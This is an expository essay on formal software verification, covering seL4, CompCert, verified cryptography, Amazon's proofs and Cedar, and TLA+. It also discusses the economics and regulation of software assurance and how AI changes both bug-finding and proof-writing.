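Language models can find faults that no analyser has a rule for, such as a shop program that applies the same discount twice. By 2026 they were finding serious flaws in widely used software. They can also explain a warning in plain language and write a fix, which addresses the problems that made Coverity abandon some of its checks. If a model can reliably discard false alarms before a programmer sees them, toolmakers can use analyses that miss fewer faults.

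False reports are still a problem when nobody filters them. In 2025 the maintainers of curl, a program that many devices use to transfer data, complained that people were sending them AI-written reports of nonexistent flaws. Later that year they fixed dozens of real faults that a researcher had found with AI tools.

Conventional analysers still have an advantage on routine checks because they are cheap and consistent. Zoncolan could process about a trillion lines a day, counting the same code again for each change. If a language model read that much at ten tokens (small pieces of text) per line and 10 cents per million tokens, it would cost $1 million a day. Reading only the code near each change would cost much less, but the model might then miss faults that span many files. Models can also give different answers on different runs, and Coverity's customers disliked even small changes in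 their results.

AI makes missed faults more dangerous because attackers can use the same models to search for them. Coverity could treat most missed faults as invisible because finding them took skilled people a long time. As the search takes less time and skill, companies have more reason to use methods that rule out whole classes of fault. Rust is the easiest of these to adopt for new code, and AI can help translate old C code into it, though someone still has to check that the new program does what the old one did.

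## Which verified components are in use, and what did they cost?

A few teams have proved that their components do what they are meant to do, and those components now run inside browsers, cloud services and cars. Their proofs go beyond what Rust's compiler can prove, which is that code uses memory safely, and what Astrée can prove, which is that a program never divides by zero. Programmers can use these components without writing a proof or knowing that one exists, so they avoid the work that put people off Jif.

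### The seL4 kernel

seL4 is an operating-system kernel, the program that controls a computer's hardware and keeps other programs apart. It leaves jobs such as storing files to programs outside the kernel, so it needs only 8,700 lines of C, compared with almost 50,000 statements in Digital's kernel. In 2009 a team at NICTA, an Australian research center, finished proving that the C code follows its specification.

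The specification describes what each request to the kernel should do. To connect it to the code, the team defined when a state c of the real kernel corresponds to a state a in the specification, written c ~ a. They then proved a rule for every step the kernel can take:

```
if    c ~ a  and the C code moves from c to c′
then  the specification allows a move from a to some a′, with c′ ~ a′
```

The kernel's starting state corresponds to the specification's. Applying the rule at each later step shows that the kernel never does anything the specification forbids. The team also proved that the kernel never crashes and always finishes a request.

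Most of the work went into proving invariants, facts that must hold before and after every request. The team proved more than 150, including that every reference in the kernel points to an object of the right type.

Trustworthy Systems, the group behind seL4, says the whole project took about 25 person-years and produced a 200,000-line proof. Designing and writing the kernel took only about two of those person-years, and much of the rest went into research and new tools. Proving seL4 itself, which is 7,500 lines of C, took 11 person-years, or about three lines per person per working day. That is no faster than the two to six lines a day estimated for specialists in the Orange Book era.

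Even so, NICTA (2009) argued that proof was the cheaper route to high assurance. It put verification at $6 million, against $87 million to take the same code to the second-highest level of the Common Criteria. The larger figure is an estimate that multiplies 8,700 lines by an industry rule of thumb of $10,000 a line. The proof would still be cheaper if the rule of thumb were ten times too high, but a buyer who needs the certificate has to pay for the evaluation anyway.

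The work needed to change the kernel varied greatly. One simple new request took a day to write and less than a week to prove. Another change touched under 5 percent of the code but took a person-year, because it broke assumptions throughout the proof.

The 2009 seL4 proof assumed that the start-up code, assembly code, C compiler and hardware were correct. *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, by Klein, Andronick and colleagues, describes later proofs that the kernel's machine code matches the C, so the compiler no longer has to be trusted. They also proved that the kernel enforces access control and limits information flow, using a form of noninterference.

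seL4 has run on an unmanned Boeing helicopter in a US military research program and in electric cars from the Chinese company Nio. Andronick, in *Successes in Deployed Verified Software (and Insights on Key Social Factors)*, credits its growing use partly to a team that combined researchers and engineers from several fields.

### The CompCert compiler

A compiler can introduce a fault when it translates a correct program. CompCert, a C compiler that Xavier Leroy began at the French research institute Inria, comes with a proof that this doesn't happen. If the C program has a defined meaning, the compiled program does only what the C program allows.

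The CompCert compiler translates a program in a series of small steps, each with its own proof that the result behaves like the input. *Lessons from Formally Verified Deployed Software Systems* (Huang, Ebersold and colleagues, 2023) puts the compiler at 135,000 lines, including proofs, and six person-years of work. It lists parsing (reading the source text at the start) and assembling and linking (building the final machine-code file at the end) among the parts that CompCert's developers left unproved.

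The company that sells Astrée also sells CompCert, which the German engine maker MTU has used for software that controls emergency generators at nuclear power plants. But most programmers still choose GCC or Clang, partly because CompCert produces slower programs. Even the HACL* team compiles its verified cryptographic library with GCC to make it faster.

### HACL* and Fiat-Crypto

Cryptographic code suits formal verification unusually well. Each algorithm is short, and a published standard defines the correct output for every input. A mistake can expose everything the algorithm protects but may affect so few inputs that ordinary tests miss it.

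HACL* is written in F*, a language that combines code and proof, and then translated to C. The proofs show that the code uses memory safely and computes what the standard requires. They also show that the branches the code takes and the memory addresses it reads don't depend on secrets, which prevents the most common timing leaks.

Huang and colleagues report that HACL* has 31,000 lines and took less than one person-year. That time excludes most of the work, because HACL* grew out of Project Everest, a five-year plan to verify the software behind secure web connections. Everest started in 2016 with 21 researchers and engineers at Microsoft and others elsewhere, who developed many of the tools that made HACL* so quick to write. Firefox has used HACL* code since 2017, and Python now uses it for several standard functions.

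The proofs can also help programmers write faster code by letting them check whether a risky shortcut is correct. HACL*'s developers made one algorithm, Curve25519, run about 2.2 percent faster than the previous record.

Fiat-Crypto, from MIT, generates the arithmetic that such algorithms need. Curve25519 works with remainders after division by the prime p = 2²⁵⁵ − 19. These numbers don't fit in a 64-bit register, so a program may split each one into five pieces of 51 bits:

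```
a = a₀ + 2⁵¹·a₁ + 2¹⁰²·a₂ + 2¹⁵³·a₃ + 2²⁰⁴·a₄
```

Multiplying two such numbers produces terms of the form x·2²⁵⁵. Since 2²⁵⁵ = p + 19, dividing 2²⁵⁵ by p leaves a remainder of 19, so the program can replace x·2²⁵⁵ with 19·x. Programmers used to work out such shortcuts by hand for every prime and every type of processor, and a single missed carry could make the result wrong. Fiat-Crypto takes the prime and the register size as inputs and generates the code. Its developers proved the generator correct in Rocq, so a new prime does not need a new proof. Google adopted the code for BoringSSL, Chrome's cryptographic library. OpenSSL's developers have also added some of it.

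### Amazon's proofs of existing code

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, wanted proofs about code it already used, so it worked with Galois, a US company that specializes in formal methods. They began with s2n, Amazon's library for TLS, the protocol that secures web connections. Huang and colleagues list more than three person-years of work on s2n for about 700 lines of code.

The next target was LibCrypto, a larger library that Amazon had derived from BoringSSL, which came from OpenSSL. Replacing it with HACL* would have meant giving up code that experts had tested and audited for over a decade. But Dodds (2022), in *Formally Verifying Industry Cryptography*, reports that existing systems are "dramatically more difficult" to verify than those designed for proof, largely because programmers have spent years making them faster.

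*Verified Cryptographic Code for Everybody* (Boston, Breese and colleagues) describes proofs for two of LibCrypto's algorithms: AES-256-GCM, which encrypts data, and SHA-384, which computes a short fingerprint of a file. Their tool, SAW, runs the code on symbols instead of real data to get a formula for each output. An automatic solver then checks that this formula always equals the one in the specification.

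Optimized code can make the formulas look very different. One part of SHA-384 takes a number a, rotates its bits by three different amounts and combines the results. Below, `>>>` rotates bits to the right, and `^` combines two numbers bit by bit:

```
Specification:   (a >>> 28) ^ (a >>> 34) ^ (a >>> 39)

Code:            t = a >>> 5
                 t = t ^ a
                 t = t >>> 6
                 t = t ^ a
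                 t = t >>> 28
```

The code rotates the original a by 5 + 6 + 28 = 39 places, the copy from the second line by 6 + 28 = 34, and the copy from the fourth line by 28, so the answers agree. The solver could confirm this in isolation but failed to use it inside the full algorithm, so the engineers gave SAW about 30 rules of this kind.

The two proofs took about nine person-months, including improvements to SAW. A reader must understand the 603 lines of specifications to know what the proofs establish. SAW checks the other 1,286 lines, so readers don't have to trust them. Other algorithms needed much more proof. AWS (2024) lists about 22,400 lines for one kind of elliptic-curve key, compared with about 1,000 for SHA-2 on Intel-type processors. AI can now produce some proofs of this sort in hours, according to *An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries* (2026).

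LibCrypto is now used well beyond Amazon's own services. Kostic (2026) reports in *AWS-LC Deploying Formally Verified PQ Crypto at Scale* that LibCrypto is the default cryptography for rustls, a widely used TLS library for Rust, and that it includes verified code designed to resist attacks by quantum computers.

### Proofs on every code change

A proof applies only to the version of the code it was written for, so it may no longer hold after the next edit. Amazon therefore runs LibCrypto's proofs automatically on every change, alongside its ordinary tests. Programmers learn of problems during code review, which is also when Facebook's developers were most willing to fix faults.

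This required a lot of engineering beyond the proofs. Dodds says teams usually allow under an hour for such checks, and often under 20 minutes, while a large SAW proof can take several hours. Galois had to split some proofs into parts that run in parallel, and sometimes had to make SAW faster. The proofs of AES-256-GCM and SHA-384 run in about half an hour.

A failed proof also blocks the release. If this happens without good reason, the programmers will probably turn the proof check off, just as they stop reading reports from an analyser that raises too many false alarms. Galois tried to avoid this by leaving as much as possible to the automatic solver, which can often redo a proof after a small edit to the code. By 2022, one of Galois's proofs had been in use for more than four years, through hundreds of changes. But some small edits still required an expert to rewrite part of the proof.

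Amazon later hid some entries in its list of proofs. In ecosyste.ms' *awslabs/aws-lc-verification*, a later copy of the front page of Amazon's proof repository, the rows for four groups of algorithms, including the elliptic-curve ones, are commented out. Amazon gives no reason there. The proofs may have broken, or Amazon may have been replacing them.

### Fixed sizes, any size and 30 to 40 caveats

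In Galois' *What Works (and Doesn't) Selling Formal Methods*, the company describes proving two versions of LibCrypto's main theorems. One covered a set of fixed key sizes and the other covered any size. They looked almost identical, but the second took nearly as much work as the first, so the total almost doubled. Galois mentions only "technical reasons", but the way SAW handles loops is probably a large part of the explanation. Consider a loop that encrypts n bytes by combining each one with a byte of a secret pad:

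```
for i from 0 to n − 1:
    out[i] = in[i] ^ pad[i]
```

If n is 3, SAW can run the loop three times and compare three formulas with the specification, which covers every possible value of the bytes. SAW can't run the loop to the end when n can be any number, so an engineer has to find a statement that stays true throughout, such as "the first i bytes of the output are correct", and prove that it holds at the start and that each pass through the loop preserves it. The engineer can reuse little of the fixed-size proof, even though the code and the specification haven't changed.

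The client therefore had to know exactly which version it was getting. Galois and Amazon agreed on a page of 30 or 40 caveats that mark the limits of the proofs. The public list from AWS names 25 in its 2024 version, including these:

| Name | Meaning |
|---|---|
| MemCorrect | The proof assumes that the functions for reserving and releasing memory work |
| GcmMultipleOf16 | The proof covers encryption only when the data's length is a multiple of 16 bytes |
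| NoInline | The proof assumes that the compiler doesn't merge certain functions into the code that calls them |
| EC_Fiat_Crypto | The proof uses Fiat-Crypto's specification of arithmetic, while the usual build runs other code, which its developers verified against a different specification |

The last caveat is a gap between two proofs. The other code comes from s2n-bignum, an Amazon library whose proofs are especially strong because they cover the exact machine instructions and so do not depend on a compiler. But LibCrypto's elliptic-curve result holds only if s2n-bignum also meets Fiat-Crypto's specification.

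Caveats protect both sides, because the client can decide which risks to accept and Galois can tell when the job is done. But Galois found that the caveats tend to disappear as people pass on the result. The client's engineers simplify them, the chief technology officer hears only the result, and the publicity team announces that the system has no bugs. When someone later finds a bug that the proof didn't cover, the client is furious.

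### Checking a model instead of the code

Amazon has also used formal methods without proving anything about the code that runs. Cedar, its language for authorization rules, is the best-known example. A rule can permit or forbid an action:

```
permit (principal in Group::"doctors", action == Action::"read",
        resource in Folder::"records");
forbid (principal, action, resource) when { resource.sealed };
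```

Cedar is a language for writing access rules, such as one that lets doctors read records unless a record is sealed. Amazon's engineers wrote a short model of Cedar in Lean and proved properties of it, such as that Cedar allows a request only if some "permit" rule applies and no "forbid" rule does. They wrote the product in Rust, then ran huge numbers of random rules and requests through both versions and compared the results. Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues report in *How We Built Cedar* (2024) that the proofs exposed four bugs and the random testing another 21.

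Cedar's guarantee is weaker than seL4's, because the tests could miss a difference between the model and the Rust code. But the engineers could write ordinary, fast Rust and change it without repairing a proof. Amazon offers Cedar through a paid service called Verified Permissions, and some products for AI agents now use Cedar.

In *Formally Verified Cloud-Scale Authorization*, Chakarov, Geldenhuys and colleagues describe how Amazon replaced AWS's authorization engine, which handles about a billion requests a second. The team wrote the new engine in Dafny, a language designed for verification, and translated it to Java. The project took four years. Before the switch in 2024, the team compared the new engine's answers with the old one's on 10¹⁵ real requests. The new engine ran three times as fast, which helped to justify the effort.

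TLA+, a language for describing designs, is cheaper still. A program called a model checker explores every order in which the events in a small version of the design can occur. Suppose two servers each read an account's balance and then write a new one. Those four events can occur in six orders:

```
read 1, write 1, read 2, write 2     correct
read 2, write 2, read 1, write 1     correct
the other four orders                one update is lost
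```

In the four bad orders, both servers read the old balance before either writes, so the later write erases the earlier one. A person can check six orders by hand, but not the millions that arise with more servers, crashes and lost messages.

*How Amazon Web Services Uses Formal Methods* (Newcombe, Rath and colleagues, 2015) reports that the TLA+ model checker found a fault in DynamoDB, Amazon's database service, that could lose data. The fault appeared only after a sequence of 35 steps, and design reviews, code reviews and testing had all missed it. The description of the design was under 1,000 lines. Engineers learned TLA+ well enough to get useful results in two or three weeks, and seven teams had used it by early 2014. But the model checker examines only a small version of the design, and a programmer can still make mistakes when turning it into code.

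### Faults in and around verified code

The best-known test of a verified component is in *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (2011), by Xuejun Yang and colleagues at the University of Utah. They used their tool, Csmith, to generate random C programs, then compiled each program with several compilers and ran the results. If the outputs differed, at least one compiler was wrong. Over three years they reported more than 325 bugs, including some in every compiler they tested.

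The researchers also found faults in CompCert, some of them in an unverified part of the compiler. In another case, CompCert produced an instruction with a number too large for the space available, because its model of the processor left out that limit. In six years of computer time, they found no mistakes in the verified middle of the compiler. The same method had found many in that part of other compilers, so this is strong evidence that the proofs worked.

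*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) reports a similar pattern in three research systems that spread work over several computers. The study found 16 faults, mostly where verified code met unverified code, and none in the verified protocols themselves. Some of the faults could crash a server or make it return wrong answers.

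A more recent dispute concerns libcrux, a cryptographic library from the company Cryspen that includes some HACL* code. *Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) reports 13 vulnerabilities in libcrux and a related library, one of which caused decryption failures in Signal's messaging protocol. Nine were in unverified code, and the other four were in specifications and proofs, including a wrong constant and a false proof about converting data to bytes.

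After Kobeissi's first reports, Cryspen wrote in *The strengths and limits of formal verification* that nobody had found a bug in the verified code. Kobeissi's company, Symbolic Software, disputed this in *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* (2026). The disagreement depends partly on whether a specification counts as verified code. If it doesn't, Cryspen's statement could be narrowly true and still mislead a customer. Kobeissi found the same kinds of gap in Amazon's LibCrypto but thought Amazon had managed them better, by documenting the limits and running proofs on every change.

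Proofs also find faults before release. Testing and student projects had found 16 faults in seL4's C code before the main proof of that code began, and the proof uncovered another 144. Many were simple typing mistakes, but some could have crashed the kernel or let an attacker in.

### What the successful components share

Five features seem to make a component a good candidate for proof, though few components have all of them:

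| Component | Small code | Stable interface | Existing specification | Severe consequences | Drop-in replacement |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | Yes | Mostly | No | Yes | No |
| CompCert | No | Yes | Partly, in English | Yes | Mostly |
| HACL* and Fiat-Crypto | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| LibCrypto | Yes, for each algorithm | Yes | Yes | Yes | Not needed |
| Cedar | Yes | Mostly | No | Yes | No |

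Cryptography does best in the table, which probably explains why verified cryptography has reached so many products. Failure would have severe consequences in every row, but that can't be enough to get software verified, because ordinary browsers also handle valuable secrets and nobody has verified them.

An existing specification matters less when the builders control the design. The builders of seL4 and Cedar had no existing specification, but they could change the design to suit the proof. During the first stage of seL4's proof, the team made about 500 changes to its specifications, and roughly half of those only made the proof easier. Galois couldn't change LibCrypto's design to suit the proof, so it depended much more on having a precise standard to follow.

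Huang and colleagues' survey of 32 verified systems supports most of this pattern. Many are compilers, kernels or libraries, and most of the rest control aircraft, trains or power plants. Programs with simple inputs and outputs were the easiest to verify. The survey found no verified graphical interface outside research prototypes. This fits the need for a stable interface, since screens and menus change often. Users rejected some verified systems, such as the mobile operating system ExpressOS, mainly because they did not work with existing software.

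Verified components in use tend to be small, but this is the least consistent part of the pattern. The software that shuts down the Sizewell B nuclear reactor in Britain has about 150,000 lines, and its verification took 250 person-years. NATS's air traffic control system has 250,000 lines and took more than 50 person-years, and its proofs mostly rule out run-time errors. Large programs can be verified when failure could kill people and someone will pay for the work. It takes less work to put a small verified component in control of a large unverified program. The research browser Quark did this with a kernel of 859 lines that controlled almost a million lines of other code, although pages took 24 percent longer to load.

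The survey is probably too favorable, because researchers rarely publish their failures. Even so, many of the projects Huang and colleagues first considered had ended at or soon after completion, and only a few systems went into constant public use. Repeating a proof after a change can take 90 percent less effort than the original, but seL4's worst small change took 17 percent of the original effort. Most of the projects relied on researchers, and seven teams said an average developer would struggle with their methods.

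## Who gains from assurance, and who pays for it?

Plenty of software that could do serious harm has never been formally verified, usually because the company that would pay for the proof expects to gain less than it costs. Mike Dodds came to this view after years of sales calls for Galois, which helped Amazon verify LibCrypto and does research on proof and program analysis, mostly for the US government. Someone who sells verification has a reason to exaggerate its benefits, but in *Proofs in the Wild*, Dodds (2024) reports that most calls end without finding any project that would help the client.

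### What clients will pay for

According to Dodds, a project happens when its benefit to the particular client outweighs the money, staff time and training it requires. Technical difficulty often isn't the obstacle. In Galois' *Specifications Don't Exist*, Dodds bets that people could verify the whole of GCC, a widely used compiler, for less than the cost of one series of Marvel films (at least $2.2 billion), but nobody would gain enough from it to pay that much.

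The benefit also has to come early. A client who has read about a successful proof may ask what a few months and a modest budget would buy. Often they would buy a set of definitions, because a team has to write specifications, learn the client's system and sometimes build tools before it can prove anything useful. When Dodds proposes a project that takes four times as long and eight times the money, most clients don't call back. Testing produces results much sooner, since a few tests will probably find a few bugs.

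Checking a design can pay off quickly too. In *The Business Case for Formal Methods*, Wayne describes a two-engineer team at eSpark Learning that had to rework a large system for an important customer. Two days of TLA+ work exposed several major bugs. Wayne values the result at $200,000 a year in revenue and $100,000 a year in saved maintenance. He led the project and sells TLA+ training, so the estimate may be generous, but the two days would have been worthwhile even at a twentieth of that amount. Computer Things' *How to convince engineers that formal methods is cool* (2024) recommends finding a bug in the team's own system as the best way to persuade skeptics. Amazon's successes persuade fewer people, because outsiders can't tell how much Amazon's systems resemble theirs.

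Many clients have already factored the cost of bugs into their business. One of Dodds's colleagues asked a leader at a maker of high-assurance systems about improving correctness, and the leader wasn't interested. The company thought its product was already more reliable than its competitor's, and it neither won nor lost sales over reliability or security. But it did want help with compliance testing. It couldn't sell the product without millions of tests, which its engineers had to write by hand, and this work delayed releases and made the team hard to staff. The same technology could have been worth a great deal to the company for reducing the number of tests its engineers had to write, even if it was worth nothing for removing bugs.

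A proof is also worth less when cheaper methods can prevent some of the same losses. Suppose faults in a program cost its owner $1 million a year. A $500,000 proof that prevented all of them would pay for itself in six months. But if $50,000 of extra testing would prevent 80 percent of the loss, the proof would save only the remaining $200,000 a year and take two and a half years to pay for itself. Some clients who ask Dodds about proof have no test suite, so it is hard to tell them that proof is the best use of their money.

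LibCrypto was different because cheaper methods had already found most of the faults they could, and so much depends on the code that the last few faults were worth removing. Dodds calls this approach "gold plating" and admits that it limits the market to a tiny number of critical components at very cautious, wealthy organizations.

### Would more training change the answer?

Another explanation is that engineers are conservative or have never learned these methods. Dodds rejects it, arguing that engineers mostly weigh costs and benefits sensibly, but surveys of experts seem to support it. Garavel, ter Beek and van de Pol, in *The 2020 Expert Survey on Formal Methods*, invited 170 specialists and received 130 replies. Each could choose up to 12 reasons why industry doesn't use formal methods more widely. These were some of the results:

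| Reason | Share of experts |
|---|---|
| Engineers lack training | 71.5% |
| Academic tools have limitations and lack professional maintenance | 66.9% |
| Developers are reluctant to change how they work | 62.3% |
| Many companies pay too little attention to quality and security | 56.2% |
| Formal methods fit poorly into standard certification | 46.9% |
| Formal methods cost too much, with no immediate value that buyers can see | 26.9% |

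The experts included three winners of the Turing Award, computer science's highest prize, but they were mostly explaining why other people didn't adopt methods that they had developed or taught. People in that position may find it easier to blame a lack of education than the cost of the methods. Their other answers are closer to Dodds's view. Only 15.4 percent thought formal methods were immediately profitable, while 58.5 percent expected a profit in the medium and long term, which is longer than most of Dodds's clients will wait. Asked where formal methods would be most useful, 77.7 percent chose generating test cases, which was the most common answer and close to what the manufacturer wanted.

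For *Formal Methods in Dependable Systems Engineering* (2020), Gleirscher and Marmsoler surveyed 216 people, 180 of whom had used formal methods in some application area. Respondents rated scalability, meaning whether the methods work on large systems, as the toughest of seven obstacles, followed by skills and education. Practitioners worried more about scalability, while people who had never used the methods in practice worried more about skills. If training were the main problem, trained people should have found fewer serious obstacles.

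Cost wasn't among the seven options, but several respondents added it. Respondents overall seemed to find formal methods useful but hard to use. The researchers recruited through online groups and personal contacts and estimated that only 1 or 2 percent of the people they reached replied, so enthusiasts are probably overrepresented.

Smaller studies also point to a lack of skills. *Survey on the Barriers to the Industrial Adoption of Formal Methods* covered 31 people at nine US aerospace organizations, including Boeing, NASA and Galois. They most often reported problems with education, with tools, and with contracts, schedules and staffing. People interviewed for *Toward Practical Deductive Verification* (2025) cited a lack of expertise and tools that were slow or hard to use.

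The shortage of trained engineers is better understood as part of the cost of assurance than as a rival explanation for its rarity. Companies pay for training when they expect it to be worthwhile. Amazon's engineers learned TLA+, and many C++ programmers have learned Rust, which is hard at first. Proof takes much longer to learn, and Dodds guesses, with low confidence, that fewer than 1,000 engineers in US industry work mainly on it. A company that wants a proof must therefore compete for scarce specialists, while students have little incentive to specialize because they see few jobs in the field. More university courses could lower the price of proof for everyone, but no single company would gain enough to fund them.

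Dodds's explanation is hard to refute, because whenever a client turns down a project, someone can say that the benefit must have been too small. The manufacturer's story is better evidence, because an engineer who just disliked new methods would have refused help with testing too. But it is a single story, and Dodds heard it secondhand.

### When someone else bears the loss

A client can weigh its own costs and benefits sensibly and still leave other people badly protected. *Why Information Security is Hard* (2001), by the Cambridge computer scientist Ross Anderson (not the Anderson who wrote the 1972 Air Force study), builds an economic account of security around this problem. It compares fraud at cash machines in several countries. When an American customer disputed a withdrawal, the bank had to prove the customer wrong. In Britain, Norway and the Netherlands, the customer had to prove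 the bank wrong, which was almost impossible. Banks in those countries grew careless and eventually suffered epidemics of fraud, while American banks had much less fraud and spent less on security.

Liability affects how quickly the bank would recover the cost of the $500,000 proof. If the proof would prevent $1 million a year in fraud and the bank bears all the losses, it recovers its money in six months. If customers bear 90 percent of the losses, the bank saves only $100,000 a year and needs five years, even though the proof is worth just as much to society.

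Anderson also explains why a software company may rush an insecure product to market. People prefer the system that most other people use, so an early lead can grow into control of the market. Strict security delays the release and makes work harder for the outside developers whose programs attract customers. A company can therefore do well by shipping early and fixing the faults in version three.

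Buyers who care about security still have to tell which products are secure. Anderson borrows a model from the economist George Akerlof. In it, a used-car market has 100 good cars worth $3,000 each and 100 bad ones, called lemons, worth $1,000 each. Buyers can't tell them apart, so they offer the average, $2,000. Owners of good cars won't sell at that price. Once buyers notice that only lemons are for sale, the price falls to $1,000.

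The same thing can happen with software. Suppose half the products of some kind are secure, and a buyer who can't tell which offers the average value, $140:

| | Insecure product | Secure product |
|---|---|---|
| Value to a buyer who could tell | $100 | $180 |
| Cost per copy | $80 | $145 |
| Seller's profit at $140 | $60 | –$5 |

The secure seller loses money and leaves the market. Buyers then offer $100 for what remains. They would have paid $145 or more for a secure product if they could have identified one, so both the buyers and the secure seller are worse off.

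Software differs from cars because most of its cost goes into the first copy. The secure product costs $65 more per copy, which might represent $65,000 of verification spread over 1,000 copies. Spread over 100,000 copies, the same verification would add 65 cents to each. The secure seller could then survive at $140, though its less secure rival would still earn slightly more. This may be one reason verification has done best in components that many people share.

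Financial Cryptography's *Ruminations on the State of the Security Nation* (2010) objects that the lemons model assumes sellers know how good their products are, when they often know as little as their buyers. It cites research in which nearly every company rated its security controls as equally effective, although the number and cost of their security incidents varied widely. Those companies were mainly users of security products, so the result shows that buyers are ignorant, but not whether sellers are. If sellers are ignorant too, they would be the first to learn from a proof. A proof helps buyers only if they can understand what it covers, and LibCrypto's long list of caveats suggests that few could.

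Independent evaluation is the usual remedy, but its value depends on who pays the evaluator. Under the Orange Book, the government evaluated products it would rely on itself. Under the Common Criteria, vendors pay commercial laboratories, so a vendor can look for the one that asks the fewest questions. Anderson had been involved in about half a dozen disputes over such evaluations and thought the system had worked in none of them. People drafting rules for independent testing of AI models will also have to decide who pays the evaluator.

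### Rules in aviation and railways

Regulators can make buyers' ignorance matter less by banning the sale of products that haven't passed an assessment. An airline can't carry passengers in an uncertified aircraft, whereas a government agency could waive the Orange Book's requirements to get a newer computer. But Gleirscher and Marmsoler found that regulators were only a minor motive for using formal methods, and that safety standards didn't require them even for the most critical systems. Wayne adds that most people who write high-assurance software don't use formal methods. Rules have mainly created demand for assurance, and proof has spread where it was a practical way to meet that demand.

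Aviation is a good example. DO-178C, the main standard for aircraft software, sorts programs by how badly a failure could affect the flight. For the most critical ones, tests must show that every condition in a decision can change the outcome by itself. Take a simplified rule for reversing the engines' thrust:

```
if on_ground and lever_pulled: reverse_thrust()
```

This needs at least three tests: one with both conditions true, one with only the first true, and one with only the second true. A decision with ten conditions needs at least eleven tests, and a flight-control program contains thousands of decisions.

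DO-333, a supplement published in 2011, explains how a company can meet some of the standard's objectives with formal proof instead of tests. Airbus had already replaced some testing of individual program units with proof on the A380. Proof could then save money on work the company had to do anyway, so fewer bugs didn't have to justify its whole cost. Dodds's manufacturer was looking for this kind of benefit.

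European railways went a little further. EN 50128, for many years the main European standard for railway software, "highly recommended" formal methods at its two most demanding safety levels, and a supplier that didn't use them had to justify its alternative. The best-known example is the driverless Line 14 of the Paris Métro, which opened in 1998. Its builders proved a mathematical model of the safety-critical software and generated about 86,000 lines of code from it. The city's transport operator bought the system, was going to run the trains, and would have had to answer for a collision, so it had good reason to care whether the assurance was real.

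The use of formal methods in American aerospace has grown steadily but modestly. In *Survey on the Barriers to the Industrial Adoption of Formal Methods*, 18 of the 31 respondents said their organization had increased its use of formal methods over the previous five years, and two reported a decrease. Certification can also discourage proof when the rules require particular tests, because a company that adds a proof must pay for both.

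### What the EU's new laws require

The European Union is extending legal duties to ordinary software through two laws it adopted in 2024. The Cyber Resilience Act covers most hardware and software products sold in the EU that connect to a device or network. Since 11 September 2026, manufacturers have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities, with a first warning within 24 hours. When the main requirements take effect on 11 December 2027, manufacturers will also have to assess security risks, sell products without known exploitable vulnerabilities, test them regularly and provide security updates, normally for at least five years. Fines can reach €15 million or 2.5 percent of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher.

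The Act doesn't require formal verification or a memory-safe language. Manufacturers can assess most products themselves. Some of the more sensitive ones, such as firewalls, need an outside assessment, but the manufacturer pays the assessor, an arrangement Anderson criticized in the Common Criteria. A company could comply through careful testing and prompt repairs, which will probably be cheaper than formal verification for most products.

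The new Product Liability Directive deals more directly with who bears the loss. It covers products put on the market after 9 December 2026 and counts software, including AI systems, as a product. An injured person must show that the product was defective and caused the harm, but doesn't have to show that the manufacturer was careless. A court can order the manufacturer to disclose evidence, and can presume a defect if the manufacturer refuses. The manufacturer can't escape liability through its terms of sale or by pointing out that a hacker exploited the defect.

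The directive covers only death, injury, damage to private property and the loss or corruption of private data. It doesn't cover a company's lost profits or a person's loss of privacy, so it excludes many of the most common results of a break-in. Someone whose medical records leak may have a claim under data protection law, but the directive gives the software's maker little extra reason to prevent the leak.

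A proof could still help a manufacturer in court, but only if the proof's specification covers the alleged defect. Manufacturers can also defend themselves by showing that nobody could have discovered the defect with the scientific and technical knowledge of the time, although member states can restrict this defense. The defense will become harder to argue as tools for finding and ruling out faults improve.

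### Does AI make assurance worth more?

As language models make faults easier to find, companies may lose more money to bugs than they had planned for. If a researcher used a model to find a critical flaw in PHP, a programming language that runs many of the world's websites, an attacker with a similar model could find the same flaw, perhaps before PHP's developers had repaired it.

Anderson's 2001 paper includes a calculation that helps here. Suppose a large product has a million bugs, and each takes a billion hours of testing to find on average. An attacker who tests for 1,000 hours a year will find about one. A defender with 10 million hours will find about 10,000, but that is only 1 percent of the total, so the defender will probably miss the attacker's bug. (Anderson gives 100,000 bugs and 10 percent, which would take ten times as much testing.)

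Now suppose AI multiplies both sides' testing by the same amount. The chance that a tester misses a particular bug after h hours is about e^(−h/1,000,000,000), which gives these results after a year:

| Testing by both sides | Bugs the attacker finds | Share of bugs the defender misses | Attacker's bugs that the defender misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anderson's figures | 1 | 99% | about 1 |
| 100 times as much | 100 | 37% | about 37 |
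| 1,000 times as much | 1,000 | 0.005% | fewer than 1 |

AI at first makes the defender's position much worse, then much better as the defender runs out of bugs to find. But the calculation assumes that all bugs are equally hard to find, that patches create no new ones, and that everyone installs them immediately. In the PHP example, the owners of a huge number of websites would each have to install the patch, and attackers could study it in the meantime.

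Anderson mentioned two ways out of this race. A new compiler might remove a whole class of bugs at once, or the security-critical part of a system might be small enough for its developers to find every bug in it. Rust is roughly the first remedy and seL4 the second, and neither depends on finding bugs faster than an attacker. But many clients will reasonably try AI bug-finders before they pay for a proof. The case for proof is strongest where users can't install fixes quickly or one missed fault would be disastrous.

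Even if assurance becomes more valuable, perhaps nobody will pay for it. Volunteers and a small foundation maintain PHP and give it away, while a serious flaw would harm millions of website owners. Each owner would gain from a safer PHP, but would gain just as much if somebody else funded the work. The Cyber Resilience Act does little to change this. It largely exempts free software that its developers don't sell, gives the foundations that support such software lighter duties and no fines, and doesn't cover most ordinary websites.

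## Now that AI writes proofs, what is still expensive?

AI also makes proofs cheaper, so some projects that made no business sense a few years ago may now be worth doing. Kleppmann (2025) argued in *Prediction* that writing proofs suits language models because their mistakes do little harm. If a model writes an invalid proof, the proof assistant rejects it and the model tries again. By late 2026, models were producing millions of lines of proof in a few weeks. But people still have to decide what to prove and make sure the statement the proof assistant checked is the one they meant.

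The models improved quickly. In Galois' *Claude Can (Sometimes) Prove It*, the AI model Claude completed many complex steps by itself but needed an expert to manage the project. According to a Lean presentation (2026), Ilya Sergey of the National University of Singapore used Claude to verify the borrowing rules of Move, a language for programs that control digital money. Sergey finished in 27 working days, compared with an estimated five to six months without AI. Claude handled the routine cases, but Sergey had to find new proof strategies.

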